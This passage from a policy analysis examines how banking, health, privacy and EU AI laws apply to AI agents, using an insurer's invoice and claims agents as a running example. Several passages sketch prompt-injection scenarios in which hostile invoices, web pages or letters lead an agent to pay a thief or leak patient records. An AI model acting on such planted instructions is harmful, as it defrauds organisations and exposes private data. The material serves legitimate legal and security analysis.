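Outcomes analysis still partly works, because the bank can count the payments that went to the wrong account. But last year's low error rate is weak evidence about this year's if a fraudster has since found text that fools the agent. Credit models also face fraud, but most borrowers aren't searching for an input that fools the model.

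The vendor can also change the model after the bank has validated it. If the vendor releases a new version every two months and the bank validates once a year, the bank will run five versions it hasn't validated before the next validation. Dimitriadis instead recommends reassessing controls after changes such as a new model, tool connection or prompt, or a broader mandate for the agent. The bank would have to decide which changes are large enough to matter, and it can do that only if the vendor tells it about them.

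Finally, validators need to know what a model is for. They can check whether a credit model predicts defaults, but an agent told to "help the finance team" has no definite task to check. If its task were narrowed to paying registered suppliers against open purchase orders, validators could test it much as they test a credit model.

### The April 2026 revision

On 17 April 2026 the three agencies replaced the 2011 guidance. The Fed's version is SR 26-2, and the OCC's *Model Risk Management* (2026) is Bulletin 2026-13. The new guidance excludes generative and agentic AI because they are "novel and rapidly evolving", but it still covers other kinds of AI model. The table draws mainly on Sullivan & Cromwell's comparison.

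| Subject | 2011 guidance | 2026 guidance |
|---|---|---|
| What counts as a model | Quantitative methods in general | Complex quantitative methods; not simple arithmetic or fixed rules |
| Generative and agentic AI | Not mentioned | Excluded |
| Frequency of review | At least once a year | No set frequency |
| Vendors' models | Evidence from the vendor, independent validation, contingency plans | Understand the model, monitor it and analyse its outcomes |
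| Board of directors | Approves the bank's policies each year | No specific duties; clear roles and accountability |
| Departing from the guidance | Non-binding, but tied to "supervisory expectations" | No supervisory criticism for non-compliance |

The agencies expect the new guidance to be most relevant to banks with more than $30 billion in assets.

Under the revision, a bank could build the safer kind of design that security researchers recommend, and the guidance would cover none of it. For example, a language model might read invoices while ordinary software authorises the payments. The guidance excludes the language model because it is generative AI, and the payment software because it applies fixed rules.

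The agencies also said they planned to issue a request for information on model risk "in the near future" that would cover banks' use of generative and agentic AI. The exclusion still stood in November, when the OCC told its examiners that the April principles apply to non-generative, non-agentic systems.

### A gap, or a return to general duties?

The agencies' exclusion of agentic AI can be read as leaving a hole in the rules. *Agent Security Meets Regulatory Reality* (Guda, Kalaga and Vishnu, 2026), by three consultants who built an agent for a consumer lender, describes the exclusion as a concrete sign of the gap between research on agents and the rules for banks. It points out that the main US framework for governing models doesn't cover the agents now entering consumer finance. *AGs warn Congress that AI threatens the financial system* (Pape, 2026) reports that federal agencies spent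 the year putting agentic AI outside their guidance, while state attorneys general want Congress to move in the opposite direction.

Sullivan & Cromwell, by contrast, doesn't read the exclusion as exempting agents from supervision, because a bank must still apply its general risk management and governance to any tool that the guidance doesn't cover. The new guidance also has a footnote warning that supervisors may act against violations of law or unsafe practices that result from poor management of model risk.

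The history of one consumer protection rule supports this second reading. Under Regulation B, a lender that refuses an applicant must give reasons that accurately describe the factors it considered. In 2023 the Consumer Financial Protection Bureau (CFPB) published a circular on how this applied to AI, then withdrew it in May 2025. As Guda and colleagues point out, the requirement stayed in force because it is in the regulation, so a bank that uses an agent to make credit decisions must still explain a refusal.

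The second reading describes the law better, but a bank that knows it is responsible for its agent may still not know how much testing would satisfy an examiner. Under the 2011 guidance, it could at least point to an annual validation. The exclusion doesn't prove that a framework for agents is impossible, because the agencies gave novelty as their reason and left room for later guidance.

Brokers have somewhat more specific guidance. Guda and colleagues report that FINRA, which regulates US brokerage firms, first treated agents as a distinct supervisory category in its 2026 oversight report. FINRA discusses guardrails that restrict what an agent can do and holds firms responsible for decisions that generative AI influences.

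### What examiners may ask

On 4 November 2026 the OCC gave its examiners *Super Intelligence* (2026), a framework for reviewing banks' use of AI. The title is the US agencies' new term for AI, so the framework covers ordinary systems that banks already use as well as hypothetical machines smarter than people. The OCC used AI to help prepare the document and says a person reviewed, edited and approved it.

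The framework has sixteen components, which the OCC groups into six pillars. Some components appear under more than one pillar. The last column of the table applies each pillar to the bank's accounts-payable agent.

| Pillar | Components | A question the examiner might ask |
|---|---|---|
| Purpose | Defined purpose and permitted use | May the agent renew a contract, or only pay invoices? |
| Risk | Risk classification | How much could it pay wrongly, and could the bank recover the money? |
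| Control | Human review, model risk management, data governance, privacy, compliance, cybersecurity | Who approves a changed account number? |
| Oversight | Governance, human review, performance monitoring, reporting | Which executive is accountable for the agent? |
| Resilience | Operational resilience, cybersecurity | Can staff pay suppliers if the bank shuts the agent down? |
| Assurance | Testing, documentation, vendor risk, internal audit | What shows that the payment limits still work after an update? |

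The OCC's main principle is that controls could become stricter as the possible consequences of failure grow. A bank may classify a system by what could go wrong, its authority and how closely people oversee it, rather than by how advanced the technology is. In the OCC's example, a simple rules-based agent that can start transactions could be riskier than a sophisticated model that only drafts internal documents. This principle matches the security argument for limiting the damage an agent can do. A bank that stopped its agent from paying unregistered accounts could argue that the restriction justified lighter controls elsewhere.

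The framework also addresses several difficulties with the 2011 approach. According to Morrison Foerster's *OCC Issues Supervisory Framework for Bank Use of Super Intelligence* (2026), a bank may document both an agent's purpose and what it is not designed to do. Some model risk principles may still be useful, but the bank can adapt them to systems that behave unpredictably or that a vendor keeps updating. Monitoring may cover both average performance and rare events that could cause serious harm. Examiners may also treat the breadth of an agent's permissions and tools as part of its attack surface, so they could ask about prompt injection without a specific rule on it.

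Examiners should assess AI under the existing risk categories rather than as a separate one. An agent that pays a thief causes an operational loss, and an agent that unlawfully refuses a loan creates a compliance problem. The bank's existing risk teams can handle both, but each team might examine only its own part of the agent's work. The OCC suggests that banks look for connections between risk categories, since one agent can affect several.

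The framework creates no new expectations for banks, and the OCC doesn't expect them to assess themselves against it. But Morrison Foerster points out that it shows what examiners may consider, so a cautious bank will probably prepare answers anyway. The framework is only a month old, so it is too soon to know how examiners will use it or what evidence they will accept.

State examiners have a similar document. *State bank examiners get a playbook for inspecting AI* (Pape, 2026) reports that the umbrella group for state banking agencies published questions, documents and risk tiers in September that examiners may use. These agencies supervise about 79% of US banks, although the four largest are national banks supervised by the OCC. PYMNTS's *Exam Prep* (2026) warns banks to expect to be asked where they use AI, which is harder to answer than it sounds. Software that a bank bought for another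 purpose may contain agents the bank doesn't know about and therefore can't assess for risk.

### What one lender had to prove

Guda and colleagues show what such evidence can look like. They built a system of agents that checks the identity of people applying for a US consumer credit product, a process called Know Your Customer. One agent coordinates four others, which verify documents, fetch credit bureau data, check the rules on bank transfers and decide whether an applicant needs further checks. The system then passes, refers or rejects the applicant.

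Before the agents, staff and simple rules handled about 100 cases a day, with a median time of two to three days. The new system resolves about four in five cases the same day and sends the rest to human reviewers, who finish within a week. Some of the referred applicants may therefore wait longer than before. These figures don't measure whether the decisions were right.

Auditors wanted the developers to show, from a single case number, exactly which factors had decided an applicant's outcome and whether the system had applied the current version of each policy. The developers had expected the main question to be whether each action was authorised. They turned their legal and audit duties into five controls. The first row of the table combines two of them.

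| Duty | Control | What the lender has to prove afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Give a refused applicant the true reasons (Regulation B) | Put the case number on every step, and check that the full record can be rebuilt before a decision takes effect | Which factors decided this case |
| Justify access to customer data (data security rules and audits) | Allow only the tools listed for the agent's role and task | That the agent could not have exceeded its task |
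| Follow current internal policy (audits) | Retrieve only approved policies that are in force | Which version the agent applied |
| Keep personal data where the lender may process it (data protection law) | Remove identifying details and free text before anything reaches the model | That no personal data reached the model's supplier |

The first version of the system fell short on several of these, and internal auditors caught problems that tests with simulated attackers had missed. The system logged its tool calls, but nobody could link the logs to particular applicants. An outdated policy made it require extra checks for customers who no longer needed them. The agents also ran under service accounts with far more access than any single case required. Nobody had misused that access, but the lender had no justification for granting it, which was enough for an adverse audit finding. The lender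 therefore needed least privilege to pass an audit as well as to limit the damage from an attack.

Guda and colleagues prove that their final check approves a case if and only if all five controls held. Otherwise the case goes to a person. The proof assumes that every tool call passes through the control layer, so it doesn't cover a script that calls a tool directly. It also defines compliance as satisfying the five controls, so it can't establish that a court or regulator would consider an approved case compliant.

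The controls reduce prompt injection but don't prevent it. The model sees only selected fields from a document, though an attacker can still put a crafted value in one of them. An auditor can detect the attack if it produces a decision that the lender's policy doesn't support. But if the false value makes an applicant appear to qualify, the record will look consistent and the check will pass. The same weakness lets a supplier bill the accounts-payable agent for work the supplier never did.

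Restricting an agent's tools can help a lender handle more applicants as well as satisfy its auditors. Suppose a credit bureau accepts 600 requests an hour. If each case needs two requests, the lender can process 300 cases an hour. An agent with too much freedom might make five requests per case, which would cut that to 120.

### Customers' own agents

Banks also have to deal with agents they didn't choose. In September 2026 Meta launched its Muse assistant, one of a growing number of tools that can act on a customer's behalf. Within weeks, several large US banks had restricted outside agents.

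JPMorgan Chase was the first of four banks to restrict outside AI agents. Chief executive Jamie Dimon said on a results call on 13 October that the bank won't let them operate in its systems until the tools it is building to protect customers are ready (Faridi, 2026, *JPMorgan Chase Restricts External AI Agents From Directly Accessing Customer Bank Accounts*). Bank of America and Citi set similar limits (Albu, 2026, *Citi and Bank of America restrict AI agents from accessing accounts*). Citi doesn't let outside agents log in or make transactions, but customers can share their account information through approved providers. Bank of America wants a person to approve money leaving an account. Morgan Stanley has also begun blocking outside agents (Mills, 2026, *Scoop*).

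The banks' basic problem was identifying who was acting, because an agent that logs in with a customer's password produces a valid login. Mills's sources said many banks couldn't determine whether a person or an agent was using an account, which agent it was, or whether the customer had asked for a given action. Some banks had seen agents that appeared to act independently of their users' instructions. Most of the "unauthorised" agents in these reports had their user's permission and broke only the bank's rule that people must log in themselves. Morgan Stanley said it had not observed rogue agents on its platforms.

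Andrew Shikiar, head of the FIDO Alliance, which develops login standards, told Daly that the restrictions were right as long as agents lack verifiable credentials. Shikiar wants each agent to carry a signed credential that identifies the person who authorised it and states what it may do. The bank could then reject any payment outside those limits, whatever led the agent to request it. The Alliance is working on such credentials with other standards bodies, but digital identity schemes in the US vary from state to state.

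Most banks have settled on read-only access or are moving towards it. This stops an agent from sending money through the bank, even if it is misled. Read-only access doesn't protect the customer's privacy, because an agent that reads account details, browses hostile pages and sends messages still has all three parts of the lethal trifecta.

The banks may have a financial motive as well as a security one, because agents could automatically move idle cash into accounts that pay more interest. JPMorgan, Bank of America and Wells Fargo hold $1.6 trillion in deposits that pay nothing. Apollo's chief economist calculated that paying 3% on that money would cost them $47 billion a year, close to half of their combined annual earnings. Albu reports that lenders have raised the risk to deposits with regulators, who have privately welcomed the restrictions. Blocking transactions serves both motives,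 so it's hard to tell from the policy alone which matters more. It will be easier to tell if agents gain reliable credentials and the banks have to decide whether to let them in.

### Who bears the loss

Bank of America said its limits would stay until it had protocols for deciding who is liable when an AI authorises a payment. US law already has rules about mistaken and unauthorised payments, though legislators wrote them with people in mind. Goodwin's *Authorizing Agentic Payments* (2026), a law firm's guide, sets out how they would usually apply:

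| Payment | Main rule | Who usually bears the loss |
|---|---|---|
| Transfer from a consumer's account | Regulation E | The customer, if they gave the agent their login |
| Consumer credit card | Regulation Z | The customer, if the agent had real or apparent authority; often the merchant, if the customer disputes the goods |
| Business payment or wire transfer | Article 4A of the Uniform Commercial Code | The bank's customer, if the bank followed an agreed and commercially reasonable security procedure in good faith |

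Goodwin considers the division of responsibility between a customer and a bank largely settled. A customer who hands over a login is responsible for what is done with it, unless the customer has told the bank that the permission has ended or the bank has broken its own security procedures.

Prompt injection makes this harder. Suppose a customer gives an assistant her bank login to pay bills, and a web page tricks it into sending $2,000 to a thief. Regulation E protects consumers against transfers that someone else starts without authority, but it excludes transfers by a person the customer gave access to (Davis Wright Tremaine, 2021). If the assistant counts as that person, the customer loses the money. However, the CFPB's *Electronic Fund Transfers FAQs* treat a payment made with a stolen or fraudulently obtained login as unauthorised. She could argue that the thief started the transfer,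 although the thief never had her login and only misled the software that had it.

Other specialists are less sure than Goodwin that the law is settled. Lande (2026), in *New Reg E Liability*, argues that agents could dramatically increase banks' liability under the same regulation. The Consumer Bankers Association, which represents retail banks, concluded after a symposium on agents' payments that it is uncertain whether existing protections apply to them. In December, PYMNTS reported that California was examining whether major banks unfairly shift losses caused by agents to customers (*California Scrutinizes Bank Terms That Put AI Agent Losses on Customers*, 2026). If a regulator or court decides that they do, banks will have more reason to keep outside agents away from payments.

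The rule for business payments matters more to the insurer. Suppose its accounts-payable agent sends a thief the $18,400 meant for Brook Cleaning. The order reached the bank with valid credentials, and the bank followed the agreed procedure, so the insurer would normally bear the loss. The insurer would have a stronger claim if the bank had agreed in writing to pay only registered accounts and then paid a different one.

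The insurer might also try to recover the money from the company that supplied the agent. Goodwin sees more legal risk in that relationship, because no statute settles what happens when an agent exceeds its authority. The outcome depends on what the customer asked for, how the agent interpreted the request and what records exist. Visa now requires companies that offer payments by agents to authenticate the user's instruction, enforce limits that match it and keep records. These requirements protect the card network, but the records would also help resolve a dispute.

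### The UK, Singapore and the EU

Some financial centres have set the scope of their rules differently from the US agencies. The UK's Prudential Regulation Authority brought in model risk principles in May 2024 for banks that use internal models to calculate their capital. Its definition of a model allows qualitative outputs, so an agent fits it more easily than it fitted the 2011 US definition. The UK also makes named senior managers personally accountable for their parts of a firm, so supervisors have someone to question about an agent even if nobody classifies it as a model.

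Singapore's approach is closer to the OCC's November framework, but it is addressed to firms themselves. In November 2025 the Monetary Authority of Singapore proposed guidelines on AI risk that would apply to all financial institutions and expressly cover agents. Firms would keep an inventory of their AI systems, assess how much each one matters and apply controls in proportion.

In the EU, the Digital Operational Resilience Act has applied to banks, insurers and many other financial firms since January 2025. It covers information technology in general, so it applies whether or not an agent counts as a model. Firms must manage technology risks, test their systems and report major incidents. When a supplier supports a critical function, the contract must include audit rights, and the firm needs a plan for leaving the supplier. Such a plan could be difficult to make if an agent depends on one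 company's model, because a replacement may behave differently even with the same prompts and tools.

European banks also have to reconcile these duties with the EU's AI Act, which treats assessing a person's creditworthiness as a high-risk use. The European Banking Authority compared the Act with existing banking and payment rules in November 2025 and found no significant contradictions, though banks may need to do some work to combine the two. This finding is useful for a bank whose agent helps decide on loans, but it doesn't settle how to test an agent that pays invoices, because that agent isn't assessing anyone's credit.

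## Do health, privacy and product-safety rules cover agents?

The insurer in the running example must also obey laws that apply well beyond finance. Suppose it sells health insurance in the United States and the European Union, and plans to add a claims agent to the one that pays invoices. The claims agent would read a customer's claim and medical records, decide whether the policy covers the treatment, and pay or refuse the claim.

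Critics who say that existing frameworks can't cover agents may mean any of three things. A law may not apply to agents at all, as when the US banking agencies left agentic AI out of their guidance on models. It may apply but give firms no test of whether they have complied. Or it may require something an agent can't do. Legislators can fix the first problem by extending the law, and regulators can fix the second by writing a test, without anyone redesigning the agent. Only the third would show that the technology itself has to change or be kept out of the work the law covers.

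### Patient records

The Health Insurance Portability and Accountability Act (HIPAA) covers US health insurers, most healthcare providers and the suppliers that handle patient data for them. It makes no exception for agents. Its security rule already requires firms to control which people and software programs can open electronic patient records.

| Duty | How an agent strains it | What the insurer could do |
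|---|---|---|
| Give access only to authorised people and programs | The agent may log in as an employee, or be able to open every claim | Give it its own identity and a credential for one claim at a time |
| Use the minimum patient data necessary | It may read a whole file to find one date, and the harness then resends the file to the model at every step | Build a tool that returns only the treatment, date and price |
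| Record and examine activity in systems that hold patient data | A log of everything the model read becomes another store of patient data | Log which records the agent opened, and restrict access to the full text |
| Bind suppliers by contract | The model, the harness and the connectors may come from different companies | Make sure a HIPAA contract covers every company that receives patient data |

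A claims agent with one defined task could meet all four duties. The minimum-use rule is much harder to meet when an agent does open-ended work, such as explaining a rise in claims costs. The insurer could give that agent de-identified records, which HIPAA doesn't restrict. A hospital is less restricted, because the minimum-use rule doesn't apply when a provider requests records to treat a patient.

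HIPAA applies to the claims agent, and the insurer can meet its specific duties, but the law's general security duty has no clear test. It requires firms to reduce security risks to a reasonable and appropriate level. That wording allows for an agent that attackers occasionally fool, but HIPAA sets no limit on how often prompt injection may succeed. If hostile text in a claimant's letter made the agent email another patient's records to a stranger, the insurer would have to argue that its precautions had been reasonable.

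### When software becomes a medical device

The US Food and Drug Administration (FDA) regulates software as a medical device if its maker intends it to diagnose, treat or prevent disease. The statute excludes administrative software, including software that determines eligibility for health benefits, so neither of the insurer's agents should count as a device. It also excludes software that advises clinicians, on four conditions:

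1. The software doesn't analyse medical images or signals, such as a heart trace.
2. It works from medical information, such as patient records and clinical guidelines.
3. It gives recommendations to a health professional.
4. The professional can review the basis for each recommendation, and so doesn't have to rely mainly on the software.

An agent that reads a patient's notes and suggests three treatments with reasons could meet all four conditions. It would lose the exclusion if it advised patients directly or ordered the drug itself. The FDA relaxed its reading of the third condition in guidance it revised in January 2026. The agency no longer intends to enforce device rules against software that offers a single recommendation when only one is clinically appropriate and the software meets the other conditions.

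The maker of a device usually has to show the FDA that it is safe and effective for a stated use. An open-ended clinical agent, such as a hospital assistant meant to "help with anything clinical", has no stated use for the FDA to assess, so it can't meet this requirement as it stands. A narrower agent built on the same model might. The FDA can also approve a plan for later changes, in which the maker describes each change and how it will be tested. That works for scheduled retraining, but less well for a rented model that its supplier may replace at short notice.

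### Prescription renewals in Utah

State licensing law reserves prescribing for licensed professionals, a requirement no AI can meet. Utah has adjusted the rule for particular products. According to the Utah Office of AI Policy's *Frequently Asked Questions*, the office can agree to change how an existing rule applies to one AI product for a limited, supervised period, but only if the agency that regulates the industry also signs the agreement.

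Doctronic, a health company, began renewing prescriptions in Utah under such an agreement in January 2026. According to *The Chatbot Will See You Now*, a summary by the law firm Dinsmore, a physician must check the first 250 renewals in each class of drug before the system can act alone in that class, and reviewers then sample about 10% of prescriptions at random.

The agreement also limits what the system can prescribe. According to *Utah Medical Board Challenges State's Regulatory Sandbox Program*, from another law firm, Hooper Lundy, patients can use it only to refill medicines that a licensed provider has already prescribed for chronic conditions such as diabetes and hypertension. Each refill lasts 30, 60 or 90 days.

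This limit does more for security than the reviews do. If ordinary software enforces it and the prescription records are genuine, a patient who types lies or hostile instructions into the system still can't get a drug that no provider has prescribed. A regulator that let an AI write new prescriptions could set a comparable limit by restricting the AI to a short list of low-risk drugs.

The reviews show how common ordinary mistakes are. If the physician found no serious errors in the first 250 renewals of one class of drug, the true error rate for that class could still be as high as about 1.2% (at 95% confidence). That limit holds only if later patients resemble the early ones and nobody is trying to fool the system. Reviewing a 10% sample is weaker still, since it has a 90% chance of missing a single bad prescription.

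On 20 April, Utah's medical licensing board strongly recommended in a letter that the Doctronic pilot be suspended, according to Hooper Lundy. Eleven of the board's 14 members signed the letter, according to the Utah Department of Commerce's *DOPL and OAIP Response to Board Concerns* (2026). The department stresses that an agreement is not an endorsement of a company's technology.

A state agreement also doesn't change federal law, including the FDA's rules. Quarles' *Utah Authorizes AI-Based Prescription Renewals* describes a bill in Congress that would expressly let AI systems prescribe FDA-approved drugs where state law authorises it. Licensing law thus does set a requirement that an AI can't meet, even one immune to prompt injection, because the law reserves prescribing for people.

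### Purpose, memory and personal data

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to almost any business agent that reads email, because names and addresses are personal data. A firm must collect such data for specified purposes and not reuse it in ways incompatible with them (purpose limitation). It must also use no more data than those purposes need (data minimisation) and protect the data with security appropriate to the risk.

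Minssen argues in *When 'agentic AI' meets data protection law* that agents with open-ended objectives pose a fundamental challenge to laws built on purpose limitation and consent. *Agentic Artificial Intelligence from the Perspective of Data Protection* (2026), guidance from Spain's data protection authority, the AEPD, suggests a practical answer. It treats an agent as a means of processing data, never as a purpose in itself, so the firm still has to decide what the data is for. If an agent replaces an employee who books travel and uses the same booking services, the firm may be processing the same data as before.

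Data minimisation likewise depends on how the firm designs the work. The AEPD gives the example of checking whether an employee is on the guest list for an event. An agent, like a human assistant, could download the whole list and read everyone's details, or ask the organiser about one name.

A customer service agent might store past complaints in memory to help it answer later ones, which means using one customer's data to deal with another. The AEPD warns that if the firm doesn't keep customers' data separate in memory, a customer might use prompt injection to extract someone else's details. The insurer could give the claims agent a separate memory for each claim, with a deletion date, or no lasting memory. The insurer must also be able to find and erase a customer's data in the agent's memory when the customer has a right to erasure.

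The AEPD adopts a version of Meta's Rule of Two as a minimum security standard. Under it, a firm should not let an email agent read unchecked messages, have unrestricted access to sensitive information and act without supervision all at once.

The claims agent would have all three properties, since it reads letters from strangers, opens medical records and sends payments. The insurer could have staff approve its actions. Under the guidance, an agent may also combine sensitive data with automatic actions if the firm can guarantee the integrity of the information it uses. A design like CaMeL, which tracks where each value came from, might help the insurer show this for payments. But a customer's letter remains untrusted even if the software labels it carefully, so the insurer would have to persuade the regulator that the letter could affect only harmless choices.

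### Decisions about people

Article 22 of the GDPR restricts fully automated decisions that have legal or similarly significant effects on a person. Refusing to pay for someone's operation is probably such a decision, but paying a cleaning company's invoice normally is not.

A firm may automate significant decisions if a contract with the person makes that necessary, if a law authorises it, or if the person explicitly consents. For health data, necessity under a contract is not enough, so the insurer would need the customer's explicit consent or a law that serves a substantial public interest. If it relies on consent, it must also let the customer give their view, contest the decision and ask for a person to intervene.

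The insurer could instead have the agent prepare each case and an employee decide it, but the employee needs the time and authority to disagree with the agent. In 2023 the EU's Court of Justice held that a credit score can itself be an automated decision if a lender relies heavily on it. An employee who accepts every recommendation from the claims agent would raise the same problem.

Regulators have made clear that firms can't pass responsibility to the software. *AI Agents Under EU Law* (Nannini, Smith and colleagues, 2026) reports that the Dutch authority warned in February about highly autonomous agents with broad access, and said the organisation that deploys one remains fully accountable. Ireland's Data Protection Commission, which leads EU supervision of several global technology companies, expects more cases involving agents (Woollacott, 2026, *Ireland's DPC reports a 'significant'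 increase in AI-related engagements*). Its *DPC statement on AI agents* (2026), published on 4 December, says it had been in talks with such companies about agents in the preceding weeks.

The GDPR clearly applies, and an insurer's claims agent with a fixed purpose can comply with most of it. The regulation requires "appropriate" security but doesn't define how much resistance to prompt injection that means. An agent with standing permission to use any record for any request can't comply, because it has no specified purpose. The insurer could fix this by narrowing the permission, but the agent would lose the flexibility that made it attractive.

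### Who answers for an agent under the AI Act

The EU's AI Act has no separate category for agents. The European Commission's *How are AI agents addressed within the AI Act?*, a page of official answers, says the existing definitions of an AI system and a general-purpose AI model are enough to cover them. It also calls the Commission's thinking on agents "only preliminary".

Suppose the insurer buys its invoice agent from a software company, which built it on another developer's model. The three companies have different roles:

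- **The model's developer** is the provider of a general-purpose model. It must document the model for companies that build on it.
- **The software company** is the provider of the AI system, meaning the agent as a whole.
- **The insurer** is the deployer. If it builds the agent itself and puts it to work under its own name, it is also the provider.

The heaviest duties apply only to high-risk systems, and a system's use determines whether it is high-risk. Nannini and colleagues conclude that an agent which reads invoices, checks them against orders and triggers payments isn't high-risk unless it also assesses creditworthiness. The Act lists risk assessment and pricing for life and health insurance as high-risk uses. It doesn't name claims handling, so the claims agent may not be high-risk unless its findings also affect a customer's premium. Paul Weiss' *Next Stop on the Digital Omnibus*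 notes that the Commission's guidelines on high-risk classification were still drafts in July.

A company's role can also change with how it uses an agent. If the insurer used the software company's invoice agent to price health cover, it would become the provider of a high-risk system and take on all of a provider's duties.

The European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026) postponed the high-risk rules in July, partly because the technical standards were late. These are the main dates after the change:

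| Rule | Applies from |
|---|---|
| Bans on harmful manipulation and exploiting vulnerable people | 2 February 2025 |
| Telling people that they are dealing with an AI | 2 August 2026 |
| Marking AI-generated content | 2 August 2026, or 2 December 2026 for systems already on the market |
| High-risk uses, such as credit assessment and health insurance pricing | 2 December 2027 |
| High-risk AI in regulated products, such as medical devices | 2 August 2028 |

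The duty to disclose already matters to the insurer. *The EU AI Act and the New Rules for Building AI Agents*, from the industry body AAIF, explains that people must be told they are dealing with AI at the start of their first interaction, unless this is already obvious. If the claims agent writes to a customer, the message should say that an AI wrote it. No notice is needed when the invoice agent exchanges data only with the bank's software.

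### Accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity

Article 15 of the EU AI Act requires high-risk systems to be appropriately accurate, robust and secure throughout their lives. They must also resist attempts by outsiders to change their behavior. That covers prompt injection, though the Act sets no acceptable attack success rate.

Nannini and colleagues argue that for an agent, Article 15 requires controls outside the model. A prompt that tells the model not to delete files isn't enough, since hostile text may override it. An agent that summarises email should therefore connect through an interface that can read messages but can't send or delete them. The article doesn't state this requirement explicitly, but they infer it from the duty to resist attack. They expect the European cybersecurity standard for AI, still a draft in April, to address it too. The inference fits the attack experiments,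 in which determined attackers kept defeating model-level defences.

A health-pricing agent built this way might have read-only access to approved records, a fixed set of tools and a person who reviews unusual prices. Its provider would also have to show that it still behaves as it did when assessed. A "substantial modification" can require a new assessment. This is a change that the provider didn't plan for in the original assessment and that affects compliance or the system's purpose.

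Choosing from a documented set of tools doesn't count as such a change if the provider tested it in advance. Difficulties arise when an agent combines tools in new ways or builds up memories that gradually change its behaviour. Nannini and colleagues conclude that high-risk agents whose behaviour drifts in ways that can't be traced "cannot currently satisfy" the Act's requirements. They propose keeping dated snapshots of the agent's tools, memory and policies, and reassessing the agent when its behaviour moves past a set limit.

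This is the strongest finding that an agent can't meet a law, but it applies only to agents whose drift nobody can trace. It also predates the July postponement, which delays the high-risk requirements for the insurer's pricing agent until December 2027. If the agent is in service before then, it stays exempt until its design changes significantly. Agents change often, so an insurer that relied on the exemption might soon lose it.

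Article 15 doesn't apply to the ordinary invoice agent, even though the agent could send a large payment to a thief.

### Known vulnerabilities

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act covers some of the agents that the high-risk rules leave out. It applies to "products with digital elements", including software sold on its own. Its duties fall on manufacturers, so the insurer would mostly benefit as a customer. Nannini and colleagues point out that the Act covers an agent that users install and connect to a network, but may not cover one offered purely as a web service. Two agents with the same weakness could face different rules because their makers deliver them differently.

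A manufacturer must not sell a product with known exploitable vulnerabilities. It must also keep a list of the product's components, test it regularly and fix new vulnerabilities without delay. Since 11 September 2026 it has had to report, within 24 hours, any vulnerability that attackers are actively exploiting. Most other duties start on 11 December 2027.

These duties work for flaws that a manufacturer can patch, but it is less clear what counts as a vulnerability in an agent. If the model's general tendency to follow malicious instructions counts, every LLM agent has a known vulnerability that no update will remove, so selling one would be illegal.

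A narrower reading is more plausible. The Act defines an exploitable vulnerability as one that an adversary could effectively use in practical operating conditions, and it ties the requirement to the manufacturer's own risk assessment. Suppose a hostile invoice can still fool the installed invoice agent, but the surrounding software blocks every payment to an unregistered account. The model still has the weakness, but an attacker can't use it to redirect the money. A missing check on account numbers would be an ordinary flaw for the manufacturer to fix, much as Microsoft fixed the EchoLeak vulnerability.

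No official standard settles the point for manufacturers. Nannini and colleagues found none planned for agents, and the working group on browsers had agreed to exclude browsers with built-in agents. Most of the general technical standards are due on 30 October 2027, six weeks before the Act's main duties begin. Until the EU recognises suitable standards, manufacturers have to argue directly from the Act's broad wording. The Act leaves some agents out and applies to others without a settled test. Compliance would be impossible only under the broader reading of "vulnerability".

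### Are LLMs a bad security norm?

*Large Language Models as a (Bad) Security Norm* (Ludvigsen, December 2025) argues that LLMs break norms that security engineers generally follow, such as not relying on secrecy, using well-proven methods and understanding every component. It gives two reasons: outsiders can't fully inspect the models, and the models give wrong answers too often. Even 99% accuracy would be too low for a security system that handles thousands of queries a second, because at 1,000 queries a second it would make ten mistakes every second.

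Ludvigsen connects these norms to the law by arguing that LLMs can't replace existing systems for meeting the Cyber Resilience Act's essential requirements, because those requirements all call for precision that LLMs can't supply. Ludvigsen makes a similar case under NIS2, the EU's cybersecurity directive for important sectors, which aims at state-of-the-art protection. Ludvigsen also doubts that anyone knows how to comply with the AI Act's Article 15, which demands defences against attacks specific to AI, because several of those attacks remain hard technical problems.

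The argument is persuasive when applied to an LLM used as the security control. If the insurer let a model alone decide whether a payment was safe, the insurer would bear the losses from the model's mistakes, and nobody could fully explain why it had approved a given payment. But the paper is mainly about LLMs that build or run security systems, and its evidence that LLMs write poor code comes from 2022 and 2023 studies of GitHub's Copilot, from which we can infer little about current models.

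The argument is much less persuasive about business agents in general. The Cyber Resilience Act applies its requirements to the whole product, so a manufacturer can use an imprecise component if something more reliable limits what it can do. The rule against relying on secrecy also concerns what a system's security depends on, and a payment limit that ordinary software enforces doesn't depend on the model. An auditor can read that software's code.

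Ludvigsen's possible solutions include adding secondary systems around the model and not using LLMs for some jobs. The paper's legal argument therefore counts against an agent that relies on its model to enforce the rules, but not necessarily against one that works within rules other software enforces.

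## Is security what holds enterprises back?

An insurer could resolve its concerns about attacks and the law and still decide against an invoice agent. The agent might misread too many invoices, the vendor register might be in an old system that is hard to connect to, or the savings might not cover the cost. People who hold the fourth view think ordinary obstacles like these explain most of the hesitation, and that firms would still hold back if prompt injection disappeared.

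### The case for ordinary obstacles

Many firms never get as far as a security review. DSIT's *AI Adoption Research* (2026), a UK government study, surveyed 3,500 businesses by telephone in spring 2025 about what had kept them from adopting AI. The most common reasons were finding no use for it (71%) and lacking the skills (60%).

Firms that do look into AI often lack the skills too. When Eurostat, the EU's statistics office, asked firms that had considered AI why they didn't use it, 70% cited a lack of expertise and only 18% said AI wouldn't be useful, according to BCCI's *Why companies that considered AI decided against it*. Cyprus Mail's *Firms boost AI use but skills shortages hold back progress* (2026) describes a euro-area study in which a lack of skills was also the main obstacle, ahead of privacy, ethics and compatibility with existing systems.

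The return can also be hard to see. In DSIT's survey, 75% of firms using AI said it had made their workforce more productive, but 77% had seen no change in revenue. Boards of African banks now want evidence that AI pays for itself, according to *The reality of banking in the agentic era* (Davison, 2026), which cites a study that the banking software company Backbase helped to compile.

However, most of these figures cover AI of every kind, including chatbots and image generators, and many of the answers come from small businesses. They are better evidence of why a shop doesn't use AI than of why a bank won't let an agent make payments.

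### How many firms use agents

Four national statistics agencies publish figures for AI use in 2026: the U.S. Census Bureau (*Large Firms With at Least 20 Employees Biggest AI Users*, 2026), Statistics Canada (*Analysis on artificial intelligence use by businesses in Canada*, 2026), the UK's Office for National Statistics (ONS) and Destatis (*Enterprises using artificial intelligence (AI) technologies, by employment size class*).

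| Country | Period | Firms using AI | Large firms using AI |
|---|---|---|---|
| United States | To early May 2026 | 20% | 37% (250 or more employees) |
| Canada | Year to spring 2026 | 19% | 28% (100 or more) |
| United Kingdom | June 2026 | 35% of firms with 10 or more employees | 49% (250 or more) |
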